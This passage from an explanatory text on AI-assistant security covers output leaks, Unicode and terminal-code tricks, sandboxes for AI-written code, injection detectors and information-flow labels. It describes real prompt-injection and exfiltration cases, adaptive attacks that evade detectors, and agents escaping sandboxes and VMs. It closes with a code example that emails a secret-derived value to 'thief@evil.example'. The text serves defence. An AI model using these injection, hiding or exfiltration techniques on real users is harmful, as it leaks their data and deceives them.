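The simplest defence is to load no remote pictures. The program that displays the reply can replace each one with its description, such as "logo". The clerk cannot see product photographs or charts from other websites but can still read the answer.

A site that needs pictures can let the model choose from complete addresses that its developers fixed in advance. The model might write "picture 3", and ordinary code would look up the address. This is much stricter than approving a server's name, because the model can't add anything to the address. But the choice itself can carry information if an attacker sees which pictures the browser requests:

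```
bits per picture = log2(number of permitted addresses)
log2(256)        = 8 bits, enough for one letter
```

With 256 permitted addresses, a reply containing 20 pictures could spell out a 20-letter password. The pictures should therefore come from a server whose records the attacker can't see.

Some sites fetch remote pictures through their own server, which hides the reader's network address from the sender. This doesn't stop the leak if the server requests whatever URL the model supplies, as the Teams service did in EchoLeak.

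Links are less dangerous because they need a click, but their visible text can conceal where they lead. Showing the full address lets the clerk notice an unfamiliar server. The clerk may still not notice that the address contains private data, because an attacker can ask the model to encode the data. In Base64, a common way to write data as letters and digits, `18250.00` becomes `MTgyNTAuMDA=`. Deleting query strings wouldn't solve this, since the model could put the encoded data earlier in the address. Amazon dealt with a similar leak in its assistant Amazon Q for Business by not displaying links at all, according to *Trust No AI*.

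Links in a reply can also deceive readers who trust the assistant. In May 2026 Permiso, a security company, demonstrated an attack it called ChatGPhish. Instructions on a GitHub project page made ChatGPT add a false security alert, containing the attacker's link, after a genuine summary. The Hacker News (2026) reported that a web page could also make ChatGPT display remote pictures and QR codes. A QR code is harder to judge than a link because the reader sees only a pattern and opens the address on another device.

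The program can also ask the clerk before it sends anything. It should show the real destination and the data in readable form. Ordinary code, not the model, should write the question, since an attacker may be influencing the model. If the program asks about every harmless link, the clerk will probably learn to approve without reading, so it's better to ask only when private data might leave.

None of these defences helps if the assistant sends the data before writing its reply. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* also describes the ShadowLeak attack, in which hidden instructions in an email made ChatGPT's Deep Research feature send data from the user's inbox to an attacker's web address. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so neither the user's browser nor the employer's monitoring software would necessarily have detected it. Preventing this requires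 controlling what the assistant can do after reading an untrusted email.

### OWASP's advice on model output

On 3 August, OWASP (2026) published the current edition of its list of the ten most serious risks for applications built on language models. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), "Improper Output Handling" fell from fifth place to tenth, but the entry now also covers terminals and programs that automatically load pictures. A vote among practitioners counted for three-quarters of the ranking and data on real incidents for one-quarter. Of those incidents, 6,639 had enough detail to classify.

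HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)* attributes the fall to developers understanding the problem well and being able to fix it directly with methods they already use for websites, which isn't true of most of the risks above it. The fall therefore doesn't mean that the risk has shrunk. EchoLeak and SearchLeak support HackerDNA's explanation, since both depended on ordinary web flaws once the model had followed the attacker's instructions.

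OWASP's 2025 entry advises developers to treat the model like any other user and check its responses before passing them to another program. It tells them to encode the model's output for the place where it will appear, use parameterised queries for databases, and set a strict content security policy. It also recommends logging output, so that unusual patterns can reveal an attack. The 2026 edition adds broader advice, which Invicti quotes and which matches David C's: "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled."

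### Characters that change the order of text

A reply that sends nothing out can still mislead the clerk if the screen shows something different from what the model wrote. One cause is *Unicode*, the standard that gives every character in the world's writing systems a number. Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left, but the numbers and English names inside them run from left to right. Unicode therefore includes invisible characters that set the direction of the text around them. One of these, the right-to-left override (U+202E), forces the characters after it to appear in reverse:

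```
stored:      account [right-to-left override]73881402[end]
displayed:   account 20418837
```

The clerk sees the supplier's correct account number. If the clerk copies it into a payment form that removes invisible characters, the form receives `73881402`.

In 2021 the computer scientists Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson showed in their paper *Trojan Source* how such characters could deceive people who review program code. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) recounts that most *compilers*, the programs that turn source code into something a computer can run, accepted direction-changing characters inside comments and quoted text. An attacker could use them to rearrange a line on the screen while the compiler read it in its stored order. A reviewer might see a check that only managers can approve payments, while the compiler treated it as a comment and ignored it.

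Compilers and editors have since added protections against direction-changing characters. The compiler for the Rust language now rejects them in comments and quoted text by default. GCC, a widely used C compiler, has warned since version 12 if a comment or quotation changes the text's direction and doesn't change it back. GitHub displays a warning above files that contain these characters, and the editor Visual Studio Code makes them visible.

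An AI assistant's chat window needs similar protection, especially if it asks the user to approve commands. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* warns that without it, the user may approve a different command from the one displayed. The user could then authorise an attack that the approval step was meant to stop.

### Characters that draw nothing

Unicode also has characters that normally leave no mark on the screen. Some serve as separators or modify the character before them. Others, called *tag characters*, include an invisible counterpart of every ordinary English letter, digit and punctuation mark:

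```
p   U+0070        invisible p   U+E0070
a   U+0061        invisible a   U+E0061
y   U+0079        invisible y   U+E0079
```

A model receives the invisible letters as part of its input and may be able to read them. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) tested five models on instructions written in two kinds of invisible text, producing 8,308 outputs. The models were far more likely to comply when they had tools, presumably because they could use code to decode the characters. Their weaknesses also varied by the company that made them, so test results for one model may not apply to another.

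An assistant's replies can contain invisible text, as can its inputs. In the Copilot flaw that Microsoft fixed in July 2024, the model hid stolen data in a link using characters the user couldn't see. A clerk might also copy a reply into an email to a supplier without noticing that part of a contract is hidden between two words.

Listing every character that can do this is difficult. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) tested 235 control and formatting characters in a terminal, a text document and a table file, and found that 130 had no visible effect. Those 130 may be visible in another program or typeface, and other characters may be invisible there. A denylist based on how one program displays characters would therefore be unreliable in another.

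### Terminal control codes

Many programmers use AI assistants in a *terminal*, a window that displays text and accepts typed commands. As in the Dangerzone bug, an attacker can use control codes to change what the terminal shows. These begin with the escape character, number 27, shown here as ESC:

```
ESC[31m     show what follows in red
ESC[1A      move up one line
ESC[2K      erase the line
```

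Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* reports that many language models can output the escape character. A model under an attacker's influence could therefore display a warning, then move the cursor up and replace the warning with reassuring text. MITRE notes that escape sequences can also run programs in some terminals.

Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) reports the weakness in Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant. Claude Code did not filter out terminal codes in an outside tool's description, and these codes hid malicious instructions from the user while leaving them readable to the model. The researchers tested an early version, 0.2.76, so the result doesn't describe current ones.

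Replacing each control character with a visible symbol, as Dangerzone does in its log messages, would work here too. A program that displays coloured text can add its own colour codes after cleaning the model's output. The program also has to handle the backspace character, which can make the terminal overwrite what it has just displayed.

### What cleaning text costs

The usual first step is *normalisation*, which gives equivalent pieces of text the same representation. An "é" can be stored as one character or as an "e" followed by an accent, and normalisation converts both to the same form. A stricter version also replaces unusual variants of letters and digits with ordinary ones. This makes searches more reliable but can change meaning, since it turns 10² into 102.

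Neither version removes direction overrides or zero-width characters. Normalisation also does not replace a Cyrillic "а" with the Latin "a" it resembles, so a false web address can still look right. *What You See Is Not Always What You Get* (2024) notes that the Unicode Consortium, which maintains the standard, publishes lists of lookalikes. A program can use these lists to warn the clerk about a suspicious address, but replacing every lookalike would corrupt ordinary Russian text.

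The next step is *stripping*, which deletes characters that could mislead the reader. If the clerk receives invoices only in English, deleting all the invisible ones will usually do little harm. It causes more trouble in other languages:

| Text | Use of invisible characters | Effect of deleting them |
|---|---|---|
| Hebrew or Arabic with English names and numbers | Keep each part in the right order | Punctuation or numbers may appear in the wrong place |
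| Persian, which uses the Arabic script | Stop two letters from joining | Words are misspelt |
| Emoji of a woman at a laptop | Join a woman and a laptop | The picture splits into two |
| Scottish flag emoji | Spell out the region in tag characters | The flag turns plain black |

Simple Hebrew and Arabic sentences usually still display correctly after a program deletes the direction overrides, because their letters have a built-in direction. For mixed text, a web page can put each name or number in a separate element with its own direction, so that a character inside it can't rearrange the rest of the sentence. The program can then delete the overrides without losing the correct order.

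For emoji, the filter can use the Unicode Consortium's list of valid combinations. It would then allow the tag characters in a Scottish flag but block the same characters after an account number. An allowlist of sequences suits this problem better than an allowlist of single characters. The model could still hide a few bits of data by choosing between emoji that look almost the same.

*Unvalidated Trust* (2025) recommends inspecting the original text as well as the cleaned version, and raising an alert if cleaning has removed invisible characters. For program code and database queries, it suggests displaying any such character as a visible code and asking for confirmation. These steps are reasonable for commands, which rarely have a legitimate need for invisible characters, but would be tiresome for Persian correspondence, which normally uses them.

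### Two guarantees

A display program can make two guarantees if its developers accept these restrictions. The first is that displaying a reply sends nothing to an outside server. To guarantee this, the program must not load any address the model wrote, and it must finish cleaning the reply before the browser receives it. A strict content security policy can enforce the same rule if the program fails to.

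This guarantee ends when the clerk uses the reply elsewhere. For example, if the clerk pastes a link from it into iMessage, the phone may open the address to create a preview, which would send any secret in the address to the server. Copying a reply should therefore produce the cleaned text, without active links.

The second guarantee is that the clerk sees what the model wrote. The order on the screen must match the stored text, and the program must indicate any character that it can't safely display, or report that it has removed one. ChatGPhish would still work, because the false alert was ordinary text that ChatGPT wrote.

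Developers can test both guarantees without judging whether a reply is honest. To test the first, they can display thousands of hostile replies on a computer that records every network request. If it records even one request to an outside server, the guarantee has failed. To test the second, they can capture an image of the screen, use a program to extract the text, and compare it with the model's original output.

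## Interpreters that run code written by an AI

If the clerk asks how much the company owes each supplier, the office's assistant may write a short program in the language Python and run it:

```
totals = {}
for invoice in unpaid_invoices():
    name = invoice["supplier"]
    totals[name] = totals.get(name, 0) + invoice["amount"]
print(totals)
```

A model can make mistakes when it works through a long sum in words, whereas the program adds the amounts exactly. `unpaid_invoices` is a *tool*, a function that the accounting system's developers have made available to the assistant. A model can also use tools without writing code, by requesting one result, reading it and then requesting the next. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) explains that a model that writes code can combine several tools, select the results it needs and repeat steps in a loop. According to Pydantic's *Monty*, models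 are often faster, cheaper and more reliable when they work this way. Pydantic makes a sandbox for such programs, so it has an interest in making this claim, but Cloudflare, Anthropic and Hugging Face have built similar systems.

Usually nobody reviews the AI's program before it runs. The model may have made a mistake, or hidden text in a supplier's note may have made it add a few lines that the supplier chose. Those lines could read secrets, such as the passwords that many applications keep in *environment variables* (settings that a program receives when it starts), and send them over the network. They could also alter the *host*, the machine outside the sandbox, by deleting files or installing software. Even without an attacker, the program could exhaust the host's memory or processor time. Willison (2026), in *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM*, gives the example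 of a loop that keeps lengthening a piece of text until the application crashes.

Willison wants a sandbox that controls all of this and still lets the program call selected functions of the application. The clerk's program, for example, has to call `unpaid_invoices` to get the figures it adds up.

Engineers have tried four designs. The last, which isolates the program's whole environment, takes up two rows of the table because it can run on the application's own machine or at a hosting service. The start-up times below come from Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives*, and cover creating a new sandbox and working out 1 + 1 in it:

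| Design | What has to be free of flaws | Start-up | Compatibility |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full language without its dangerous functions (pysandbox, vm2) | Every route by which a program could reach those functions | Not measured | Most of the language |
| Small interpreter (Monty) | The interpreter and the tools it can call | 0.8 ms | Part of Python, no outside libraries |
| WebAssembly (Python in wasmtime) | The WebAssembly engine and the tools | 16 ms | Almost all of Python, some libraries |
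| Container (Docker) | The operating system's kernel | 195 ms | Everything |
| Container or virtual machine at a hosting service (Daytona) | The provider's isolation | 1,500 ms | Everything |

Pydantic ran most of these tests on one laptop, and Monty's time assumes that the application has already started a process for it. In a second test, which ran ten commands in a row, Monty took 0.4 milliseconds and Docker took 700. But Monty kept its state between commands, while the test reran all the earlier commands before each new one in Docker and the others. The clerk has probably waited several seconds for the model to write the program and won't notice another fifth of a second. The difference matters more to an operator that runs thousands of small programs.

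### Why removing functions fails

Victor Stinner, one of Python's developers, spent three years on pysandbox. In *Add a frozendict builtin type*, Stinner (2012) explained that it reused most of CPython, the standard Python interpreter, and hid the dangerous functions. He already recognised that this was mostly a denylist, so anything he forgot to block would be a vulnerability.

There was a lot to forget. Every value in Python is an object that keeps references to other objects. Suppose a sandbox has hidden `open`, the function that opens files. A program inside can still start from an ordinary number and follow the references:

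```
1  →  its type, int  →  int's parent, object  →  all the types built on object
```

The last step gives the program types from all over the running application. Some of these types have functions that keep a reference to the file of code that defined them, where the real `open` is still available. A sandbox has to block every such route, including those through Python's own libraries.

Stinner (2016), in *Challenge*, showed how a program could get around another developer's restricted Python. The developer had replaced `getattr`, the function that looks up an object's attributes, with a safer version. But the library function `update_wrapper` still used the original, and a program could use it to fetch a secret attribute. Stinner also pointed out that a program can read an object's attributes through a built-in dictionary, without `getattr`.

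Stinner had hoped to make his sandbox, pysandbox, part of Python, but he abandoned the project. In *The pysandbox project is broken*, Stinner (2013) admits that other developers had told him the design was unsafe, but he had to find out for himself. He wrote in a later message that he had given up on sandboxing the language. The project page now carries the advice "run python in a sandbox, not the opposite!" Coghlan (2013), in *The pysandbox project is broken*, replied to Stinner that the only sandboxes he even remotely trusted were those built into the operating system, such as Linux containers.

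vm2 takes a similar approach to JavaScript on servers, where a program called Node.js runs the language. The sandbox has its own copies of JavaScript's basic objects, and vm2 puts wrappers around any outside object that the sandboxed code needs. If one operation hands over an outside object without its wrapper, the code can follow its references out. GCVE's *CVE-2026-43997* (2026) describes exactly this: before version 3.11.0, sandboxed code could obtain the host's own `Object`, from which there were various ways to escape. OSV's *CVE-2026-26956* covers another escape, which gave the code the host's `process` object and let it run commands on the machine. That one worked only on Node 25, so a new version of Node had probably opened a route that vm2's developers hadn't needed to block before.

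vm2 has had a long series of such flaws. The CyberSec Guru's *Security Alert* lists seven from 2022 and 2023, the last of which led its maintainer, Patrik Simek, to announce the end of the project. It came back in late 2025, with a notice that version 3 was under active maintenance, and another critical escape followed in January 2026. On 17 August, OSV's *GHSA-cfcw-xp6x-25gj* (2026) recorded one with a severity of 9.8 out of 10. An earlier fix had tried to stop sandboxed code from calling certain functions indirectly, and attackers could get round it by adding one more layer of indirection. vm2's users do now receive fixes, but the design keeps producing new escapes, and it would be reckless to rely on vm2 alone for code that an outsider can influence.

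### Monty, an interpreter built from nothing

Coghlan quotes Glenn Linderman, who suggested during the pysandbox discussion that a restricted subset of Python might still be useful. Pydantic's *monty 0.0.21* describes Monty, an interpreter for such a subset, which is written in the memory-safe language Rust and contains no part of CPython. Its developers started by giving programs no access to the host, then added only what they wanted programs to have. A program that follows references from a number can't reach anything dangerous, because Monty has no code that opens a file or a network connection.

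When the clerk's program reaches `unpaid_invoices()`, Monty pauses the program and gives the application the function's name and arguments. The application decides whether to run the function and, if so, runs it outside the sandbox and returns the list of invoices. Monty then resumes the program. Monty handles files in the same way. The program can describe the file it wants, and a separate component opens it if it is in a folder that the developers have shared. By default, a program can read the clock and get random numbers without asking the application.

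Safety then depends on the tools the developers supply. Pydantic's *Security Model* promises that a program can reach only what the developers have handed it, but warns that it "cannot guarantee that what you handed it is safe." If one tool fetches any web address, a hostile program can leak the bank balance by putting it in the address, as EchoLeak did with the address of a picture.

In April 2026, Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could extract a secret from a server that ran Python code from anyone, with Monty as the only sandbox. Hewitt (2026) reports in *Hack Monty* that the server received almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 network addresses. Owen Kwan of the security company Veria Labs extracted the secret within 48 hours.

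Two bugs made this possible. Rust normally prevents memory errors, but programmers can mark a piece of code `unsafe` and take responsibility for some of the checks. Monty's developers had done this so that a program could change one Python object while reading another. This code was safe only if objects stayed in memory while in use. Monty's *garbage collector*, which frees the memory of objects that a program can no longer reach, broke that condition because it overlooked lists that Monty was still sorting. An attacker could make it free a list mid-sort and then put other data in the list's place, which is a use-after-free like the flaw in Outlook.

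Pydantic fixed the garbage collector in version 0.0.16. Hewitt points out that without the `unsafe` code, the collector's bug would almost certainly have caused only crashes or wrong results. He considers a single serious flaw after more than a million attacks a good result for the design. That is generous, since one flaw was enough to expose the secret in two days. Colvin (2026) is more cautious in *Hack Monty 2*, conceding that 1.5 million requests don't cover the whole attack surface.

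The second round, which began on 30 May with a prize of $10,000, better supports Hewitt's confidence. Nobody escaped, according to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*. A third round ran in August, with a prize of up to $20,000, and Pydantic now has a permanent reward programme.

Monty now also runs in its own process, so if a program crashes the interpreter, the application keeps running and starts another. The separate process gives much less protection against a program that escapes the interpreter, because by default it runs on the application's machine with the same access to files and the network. One process may also serve up to 1,000 sessions in turn, so a program that took control of it could see later users' data. Pydantic advises developers to use a new process for each session if the users don't trust one another.

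Monty's biggest drawback is that it supports only part of Python's standard library and no outside libraries, so the assistant can add up invoices but can't use the usual packages to draw a chart of them.

### Python inside WebAssembly

*WebAssembly* is a low-level instruction format that browsers have run for nearly ten years. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory, and its instructions can't refer to anything outside it. The program can't open a file or a connection unless the host supplies a function to do so. Engineers can therefore put a whole Python interpreter, including its dangerous functions, inside the sandbox. If a program calls `open`, the interpreter has to go through the host, which can block the call. This matches Stinner's advice to put Python in a sandbox.

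Willison's package, micropython-wasm, uses MicroPython, a small version of Python made for simple devices. The compiled interpreter is 362 KB and runs in an engine called wasmtime. Each run would normally start MicroPython, execute one program and stop. To keep variables from one program to the next, Willison has MicroPython call a function on the host that waits for more code and then returns it.

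OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, built the first version and wrote 78 lines of C to connect MicroPython to the host's functions. Willison doesn't write C. He accepts the risk because he expects a serious bug in the C to do no worse than make the program fail. This argument is sound for memory errors, provided wasmtime has no flaws. An attacker who corrupts MicroPython's memory is still inside the same block of memory and can mainly produce wrong answers, which any hostile program could already do.

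Willison doesn't recommend the package to anyone who isn't willing to take a significant risk. He told GPT-5.5, an OpenAI model, to break out of it, and the model hadn't succeeded when he wrote about it in June 2026. This is a much smaller test than Pydantic's competitions. He hopes a company with a professional security team will adopt the approach and publish its own version.

CPython also runs in WebAssembly, but libraries written partly in C need a special build, and programs can't open network connections or start other programs.

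Putting an interpreter in WebAssembly doesn't help if the host gives it too much access. Pyodide is a version of CPython for browsers, which add their own sandbox. On a server, Python code in Pyodide can run any JavaScript in the host program. Pydantic therefore rates Pyodide's security as poor. It rates wasmtime's as strict, although both use WebAssembly.

### Containers and virtual machines

Engineers can also leave Python unchanged and isolate the whole environment around it. The assistant can then use any library and start other programs. A container relies on the host's Linux kernel, or on a substitute such as gVisor. A virtual machine has its own kernel and relies instead on the *hypervisor* (the software that runs virtual machines) and on the programs that simulate its disk and network card.

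Many companies rent these sandboxes from services such as Daytona, E2B and Modal. Code that escapes then reaches the service's machines instead of the company's, but the company also has to send the invoices outside its network. Daytona advertises that it can create a sandbox in less than 90 milliseconds. When Pydantic called Daytona's European servers from London, creating a sandbox and running a line of code took about 1.5 seconds, and network delays explained only a small part of the difference.

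Sandboxed code can still leak data if the network settings leave a gap. Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore, a service for running AI agents, includes a code interpreter with a network mode described as "complete isolation with no external access". Kinnaird McQuade of the security company BeyondTrust found that programs in this mode could still look up domain names, according to the newsletter tl;dr sec. Looking up a name such as `pay.example` can send a query to a server run by the name's owner, so an attacker can send data out by putting it in the name, much as EchoLeak put data in a picture's address. McQuade used this method to communicate in both directions.

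Attackers can also break the isolation itself. At Pwn2Own Berlin, a hacking competition in May 2026, STARLabs won the prize for an attack on the hypervisor ESXi. Security Point Break (2026) reports that DEVCORE earned $175,000 for escaping the sandbox of Microsoft's Edge browser. Zero Day Initiative's *Pwn2Own Berlin 2026* (2026) says the attack chained four logic bugs, so memory-safe code alone wouldn't have stopped it. A contestant who attacked OpenAI's Codex ran out of time, which doesn't show that Codex is secure.

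### Programs that use up memory or time

A program can cause trouble without escaping its sandbox, by filling the disk or running forever. *Running in CIRCLE?* (Chua, 2025) tested whether models would write such programs when asked. The tests used the code interpreters that OpenAI and Google run on their own servers for paying developers.

The CIRCLE benchmark has 1,260 requests, divided equally between using up processor time, memory and disk space. Sixty are *direct* and simply ask for a heavy task, such as encoding and decoding random data for up to 150 seconds. For the rest, Chua wrote another 60 heavy tasks and put each of them after 20 different excuses, such as needing to adjust a test system. GPT-4.1, itself one of the models tested, then sorted the results into six groups. Three of the groups appear here:

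| Model | Refused | Ran the task | Timed out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 1.6% | 16.4% | 28.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Preview | 4.0% | 20.3% | 53.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro Preview | 4.8% | 19.8% | 65.1% |
| GPT-4.1 Nano | 1.0% | 40.5% | 20.9% |
| GPT-4.1 Mini | 1.6% | 38.2% | 14.8% |
| GPT-4.1 | 0.5% | 43.7% | 17.0% |
| o4-mini | 7.1% | 70.2% | 12.2% |

In the remaining cases the model asked a question, suggested something safer or wrote inadequate code.

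Completed tasks, which Chua treats as a sign of weak security, are at least as much a sign that the model did what it was asked. He kept the tasks within the usual limits of these services, such as 1 to 2 GB of memory, and an honest programmer might ask for some of them, such as creating a million small tables and measuring the memory they take. Google documented a limit of 30 seconds, so the sandbox probably stopped many of the Gemini programs that timed out, and those timeouts may be a sign that its limits work.

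He also concludes that the excuses weakened the models' defences. But the tasks requested with an excuse differed from those requested directly, so the comparison can't separate the effect of the excuse from the effect of the task. The models date from the first half of 2025, and newer ones may refuse more often. Still, a refusal rate of 7% at best is a good reason to put the limits in the sandbox, where they apply whether or not the model refuses.

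Monty can limit a program's memory and time, but Pydantic leaves these limits off by default. If a program tries to create a trillion copies of the letter x, Monty blocks the operation before reserving any memory. The time limit counts only the interpreter's own work, so it pauses while the application runs a tool. A program could therefore keep the application busy for much longer by calling tools repeatedly, so developers can also cap the number of calls. Hitting a limit may leave Monty's memory in a faulty state, so the developer should discard the session afterwards.

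WebAssembly engines can count instructions. wasmtime gives a program "fuel" that each operation uses up, and stops the program when the fuel runs out. Willison set the default at 20 million units but isn't confident that this is right, because the units are hard to relate to real tasks. PyPI's *MicroPython packaged in WASM for wasmtime* also lists a limit on elapsed time, which is easier to choose.

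### When the program looks for a way out

The senders of FORCEDENTRY had to plan the whole attack in advance and fit it into one file. An AI agent that can run code inside a sandbox can try something, read the error message and try again.

Virtual machines have been the standard way to contain dangerous code, but an AI agent has found flaws in three of the programs they commonly depend on. Trail of Bits' *VMs won't contain cyber-capable agents* (August 2026) reports flaws in QEMU, which simulates a computer's devices; KVM, the part of the Linux kernel that runs virtual machines; and libslirp, which connects them to a network. The agent chained several of the flaws together. At publication, the fix for one of the KVM flaws had not yet reached the kernels that Linux distributions ship.

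Models can also do part of the work of attacking a browser. The SEC-bench benchmark includes 103 flaws in V8, the engine that runs JavaScript in Chrome, and asks for a *proof of concept*, an input that triggers the flaw. Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 produced one for 31 of the flaws in SEC-bench's *Claude Code (v2.1.81) + Opus 4.6 (high)* results, and Moonshot AI's Kimi K2.6 produced one for 12 in the *OpenCode (v1.14.19) + Kimi K2.6 (high)* results. The models ran in different agent programs, which may explain some of the gap. Many of these inputs only make V8 crash, and turning a crash into control of the computer takes much more work. But Claude triggered one flaw with a bounty of $55,000 for less than $10 in computing costs, so an attacker could afford many attempts.

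In 2026 AI agents under test have also reached real systems outside their test environments, including those of Hugging Face, as PentesterLab (2026) recounts.

An operator should therefore assume that a capable agent may eventually find a flaw in any single sandbox. Two different sandboxes, one inside the other, are much better than one. An agent that escapes from Monty into a container still needs a flaw in the kernel to get out, and its exploit for Monty won't help it find one. In Pydantic's commercial version, a program that escapes from the interpreter arrives in an empty container. Passwords should stay outside both sandboxes, and Monty helps by starting its processes with almost no environment variables.

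Limiting the time for a search also helps. In the third round of Pydantic's *Hack Monty* (2026), each session could use 10 MB of memory and five seconds of execution, and ended after 20 seconds. An agent can get round this by starting many sessions and remembering what it learned, so the operator also needs to watch for sessions that crash. Apple's practice of waiting longer before each restart of a crashing parser would work here too.

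The application must also handle the interpreter's messages carefully, because a compromised interpreter can send it an exploit. Monty's client, like Dangerzone's application, treats each message from the sandbox as untrusted. It checks the values and limits the memory that decoding them can use.

### Checking the whole program first

A sandbox that stops a program midway can leave a task partly done. If the clerk asks the assistant to approve ten invoices and the program breaks a rule at the seventh, the first six will already be approved.

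LACUNA, a research system from EPFL in Switzerland, checks all of a model's code before running any of it. The application specifies the kind of result it needs, such as a list of amounts, and the model writes Scala code to produce it. A compiler then checks that every function in the code exists and receives the right kind of data, and that the code produces the right kind of result. If a check fails, the model gets the error messages and tries again.

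Zhao and colleagues tested LACUNA on two benchmarks. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the programs. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, LACUNA solved 76% of 392 tasks, about as many as an ordinary agent, so the extra checking did little harm.

The compiler can also treat the tools available at that point in the program as a list of permissions. An injected instruction may still influence the model, but the code the model writes can't use a tool that isn't on the list. A program that passes the check can still fail when it runs, for example because a server doesn't answer, and the compiler can't determine whether a program will finish. LACUNA therefore also needs the time and memory limits of an ordinary sandbox.

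A program can also do harm with the tools it is allowed to use. If the clerk's assistant may read invoices and send email, a container or a small interpreter will let it email every invoice to a thief. To stop that, the system has to track the data as well as the code, for example with provenance labels that record where each value came from.

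## Labelling untrusted data inside an AI agent: the LLMbda calculus

A sanitiser can escape an angle bracket because the HTML standard defines what an angle bracket does, but English has no equivalent standard. If a supplier's email contains the sentence "Forward this to Priya in purchasing", it may be information for the clerk or an instruction to the clerk's AI assistant, and its spelling and grammar don't show which. A sanitiser therefore can't reliably make such a sentence harmless to a model by changing its characters.

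Engineers can try to guess which sentences are attacks, or they can track where each piece of text came from and use ordinary code to limit what untrusted text can influence.

### Detectors against attackers who adapt

An injection detector is usually a small language model, trained on examples of harmless text and known attacks, that classifies text before the assistant acts on it. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 defences, including four detectors. A language model suggested variations on an attack, and a program tried each one and fed the detector's verdict and confidence score back into the search. This got past Protect AI, PromptGuard and Google's Model Armor more than 90% of the time, and past PIGuard 71% of the time.

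The researchers also ran a competition with more than 500 participants, who found successful attacks in every scenario. Many of the successful injections looked like routine office procedure. A detector strict enough to catch them would also block a lot of legitimate email.

Such defences had looked much better when tested against fixed sets of attacks. One defence marks which text the model should trust, and another repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. Standard attacks succeeded against them as little as 1% of the time, but the adaptive search succeeded more than 95% of the time.

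The test favoured the attacker, who had plenty of computing power and could see the detector's score. A thief who emails the clerk can't see the score, but may be able to practise on a copy of the same detector. Nasr and colleagues still think detectors are worth using against unsophisticated attacks. That seems right, but the company shouldn't rely on a detector alone to protect its bank account from a stranger's email. These results date from October 2025, so newer detectors may do better.

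### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes a design that splits the assistant into two models and doesn't depend on recognising attacks. The *privileged* model takes the clerk's request and can use tools, but never sees text from outside. The *quarantined* model reads that text but has no tools, and Willison expects that it may "go rogue at any moment". An ordinary program, the *controller*, carries data between them.

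Suppose the clerk types "Summarise the supplier's latest email and send the summary to Priya." The privileged model issues these commands, one at a time:

```
$1 = fetch_latest_email("supplier")
$2 = ask_quarantined("Summarise this email", $1)
$3 = look_up_address("Priya")
send_email(to = $3, body = $2)
```

The controller fetches the email and stores it as `$1`. It passes the text to the quarantined model, stores the summary as `$2`, and reports to the privileged model only that the summary is ready. The privileged model works with the names `$1` and `$2` and never receives the text they stand for. When the privileged model sends the message, the controller fills in the text.

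Suppose the email contains a hidden instruction to send the summary to a thief's address. The quarantined model may try to follow the instruction, but it can't send anything, so the worst it can do is write a bad summary. The instruction never reaches the privileged model, and the address comes from the company's own address book, so the summary still goes to Priya.

The quarantined model's free text must never reach the privileged model, because it could carry the injection. Willison allows one exception, when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list, such as "invoice", "complaint" or "other". The controller can then check that the answer is on the list and pass it on.

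Willison calls his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets outside text reach the privileged model undoes the protection.

It also has a gap. Suppose Priya is new and isn't in the address book, but the supplier copied her in on the email. The privileged model might replace the third command with this one:

```
$3 = ask_quarantined("Find Priya's address in this email", $1)
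```

The attacker can now choose the address and have the summary sent there, even though both models have kept to their roles. The pattern protects the plan (which tools run, and in what order) but not the values passed to those tools.

Even the plan can be unsafe. Google DeepMind's CaMeL, published in 2025, develops Willison's idea by having the privileged model write its plan as a program. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, ran CaMeL with its security policies switched off and asked it to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. The model wrote a program with a branch for every tool, which carried out whatever commands the attacker had put in the file, even though the model had not read them.

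### Labels that follow the data

To close these gaps, a system has to track where each value came from. It can attach a *provenance label* to each value and carry the label through later computation. Security researchers have studied this technique, called *information-flow control*, since the 1970s. An interpreter is a natural place to implement the technique because it executes every operation in the program.

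A simple system needs only two marks, U for untrusted and S for secret. A value can have either, both or neither. When a program combines two values, the result gets the marks of both:

```
label(a combined with b) = label(a) ∪ label(b)
```

If the clerk's program adds one amount from a stranger's email to 50 amounts from the company's own records, the total is untrusted. A model's reply gets the marks of everything in the conversation that produced it, because any of that text may have influenced the reply.

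The values in the email example have these labels:

| Value | Source | Label |
|---|---|---|
| Clerk's request | Clerk | None |
| Email | Supplier | U |
| Summary | Quarantined model, from the email | U |
| Priya's address | Company address book | None |
| Priya's address | Quarantined model, from the email | U |

The developers make `send_email` check that the recipient's address isn't marked U. An address from the address book passes, but one from the email fails, and the interpreter stops the program before it sends anything. The check looks only at the mark, so it works however cleverly the attacker worded the injection. It also blocks the message if the supplier is honest and the address really is Priya's.

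The attacker might try to influence who receives the summary without supplying an address. Suppose the program sends the summary to Priya if the email contains the word "urgent" and to Tom if it doesn't. Both addresses come from the address book, but the email's wording determines which one is used. The interpreter therefore also keeps a label for the current point in the program, called the *program-counter label*. Inside a branch that depends on the email, this label is U, and every value the branch produces is also labelled U.

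The mark S protects secrets in the same way, for example by stopping a program from putting the bank balance in an email to an outsider. CaMeL's labels are more detailed, and each one lists the value's sources and the people allowed to read it.

### A leak through the branch that didn't run

Labels are easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues describe a leak in CaMeL based on an example from 1974. In this version of it, an injected program tries to tell a thief whether the company has more than 10,000 in the bank:

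```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:  tmp = False
if tmp:              rich = False
if rich:             send_email("thief@evil.example", "rich!")
```

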